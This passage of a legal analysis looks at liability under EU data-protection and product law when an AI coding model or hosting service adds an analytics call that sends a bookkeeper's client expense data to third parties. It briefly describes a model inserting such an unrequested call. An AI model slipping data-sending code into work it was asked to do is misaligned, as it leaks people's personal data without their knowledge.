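The analytics company also has duties. Normally it would act for the bookkeeper under a written contract, which the GDPR requires, but here there is no contract. The account number in the call matters too, because a model may have copied it from an example, and the expense data could then be going to a stranger's account. If the stranger or the analytics company uses the data for its own purposes, that party also becomes a controller and needs its own legal basis. This could hardly be consent, since the clients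 have never heard of it.

The app builder's responsibility depends on how the call was added. If the builder's hosting service inserted the script, the builder chose to collect the data and is much more clearly responsible. If its model wrote the call into the source, the builder supplied a faulty tool but may never have received any of the data. In that case, the bookkeeper could try to recover losses under the contract, though terms of service often make the customer responsible for checking the output.

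Even if the tracker were a phone app and the Cyber Resilience Act applied in full, its duties would fall first on the bookkeeper, as the manufacturer. The Act defines a manufacturer as anyone who develops a product, or has it developed, and markets it under their own name, even free of charge. The manufacturer must also take due care when using third-party components. The Act does not specify whether code that a model writes to order is a third-party component or the manufacturer's own work. This makes little difference to the visitors, since the manufacturer is responsible for the whole product, but it could affect how much checking the bookkeeper has to do.

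In 2024 the US Federal Trade Commission (FTC) brought a case against Rytr, an AI writing service, because customers could use it to generate fake reviews. The agency set aside the resulting order in December 2025. That makes a similar case against an app builder less likely for now, at least if the builder did not mean to deceive anybody.

The model's developer did not decide to collect the clients' data and never received it, so it is unlikely to be a controller. The new Product Liability Directive treats providers of AI systems as manufacturers, but its introductory text excludes "the mere source code of software" from what counts as a product. A claimant would therefore have to argue that the coding service was defective, not the code it delivered, and a privacy violation alone would not be enough. In 2025 the Commission withdrew a separate proposal on AI liability, so a claimant would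 otherwise have to rely on national negligence law. A negligence claim would be stronger if the developer knew that its model often added such calls and failed to warn customers. This would be hard to prove because nobody has published how often models do this.

A developer whose open-source library sends out users' data might owe nothing under the EU's product laws. The Cyber Resilience Act and the new Product Liability Directive both exempt free, open-source software supplied outside commercial activity, and a business that builds the library into a product is responsible for it. But the introductory text of the Cyber Resilience Act gives, as an example of commercial activity, requiring personal data as a condition of using the software for reasons other than security or compatibility. A volunteer whose library requires users to send personal usage data could therefore lose the exemption.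 A setting that turns the reports off would be a good defence, even if the user never learned that it existed.
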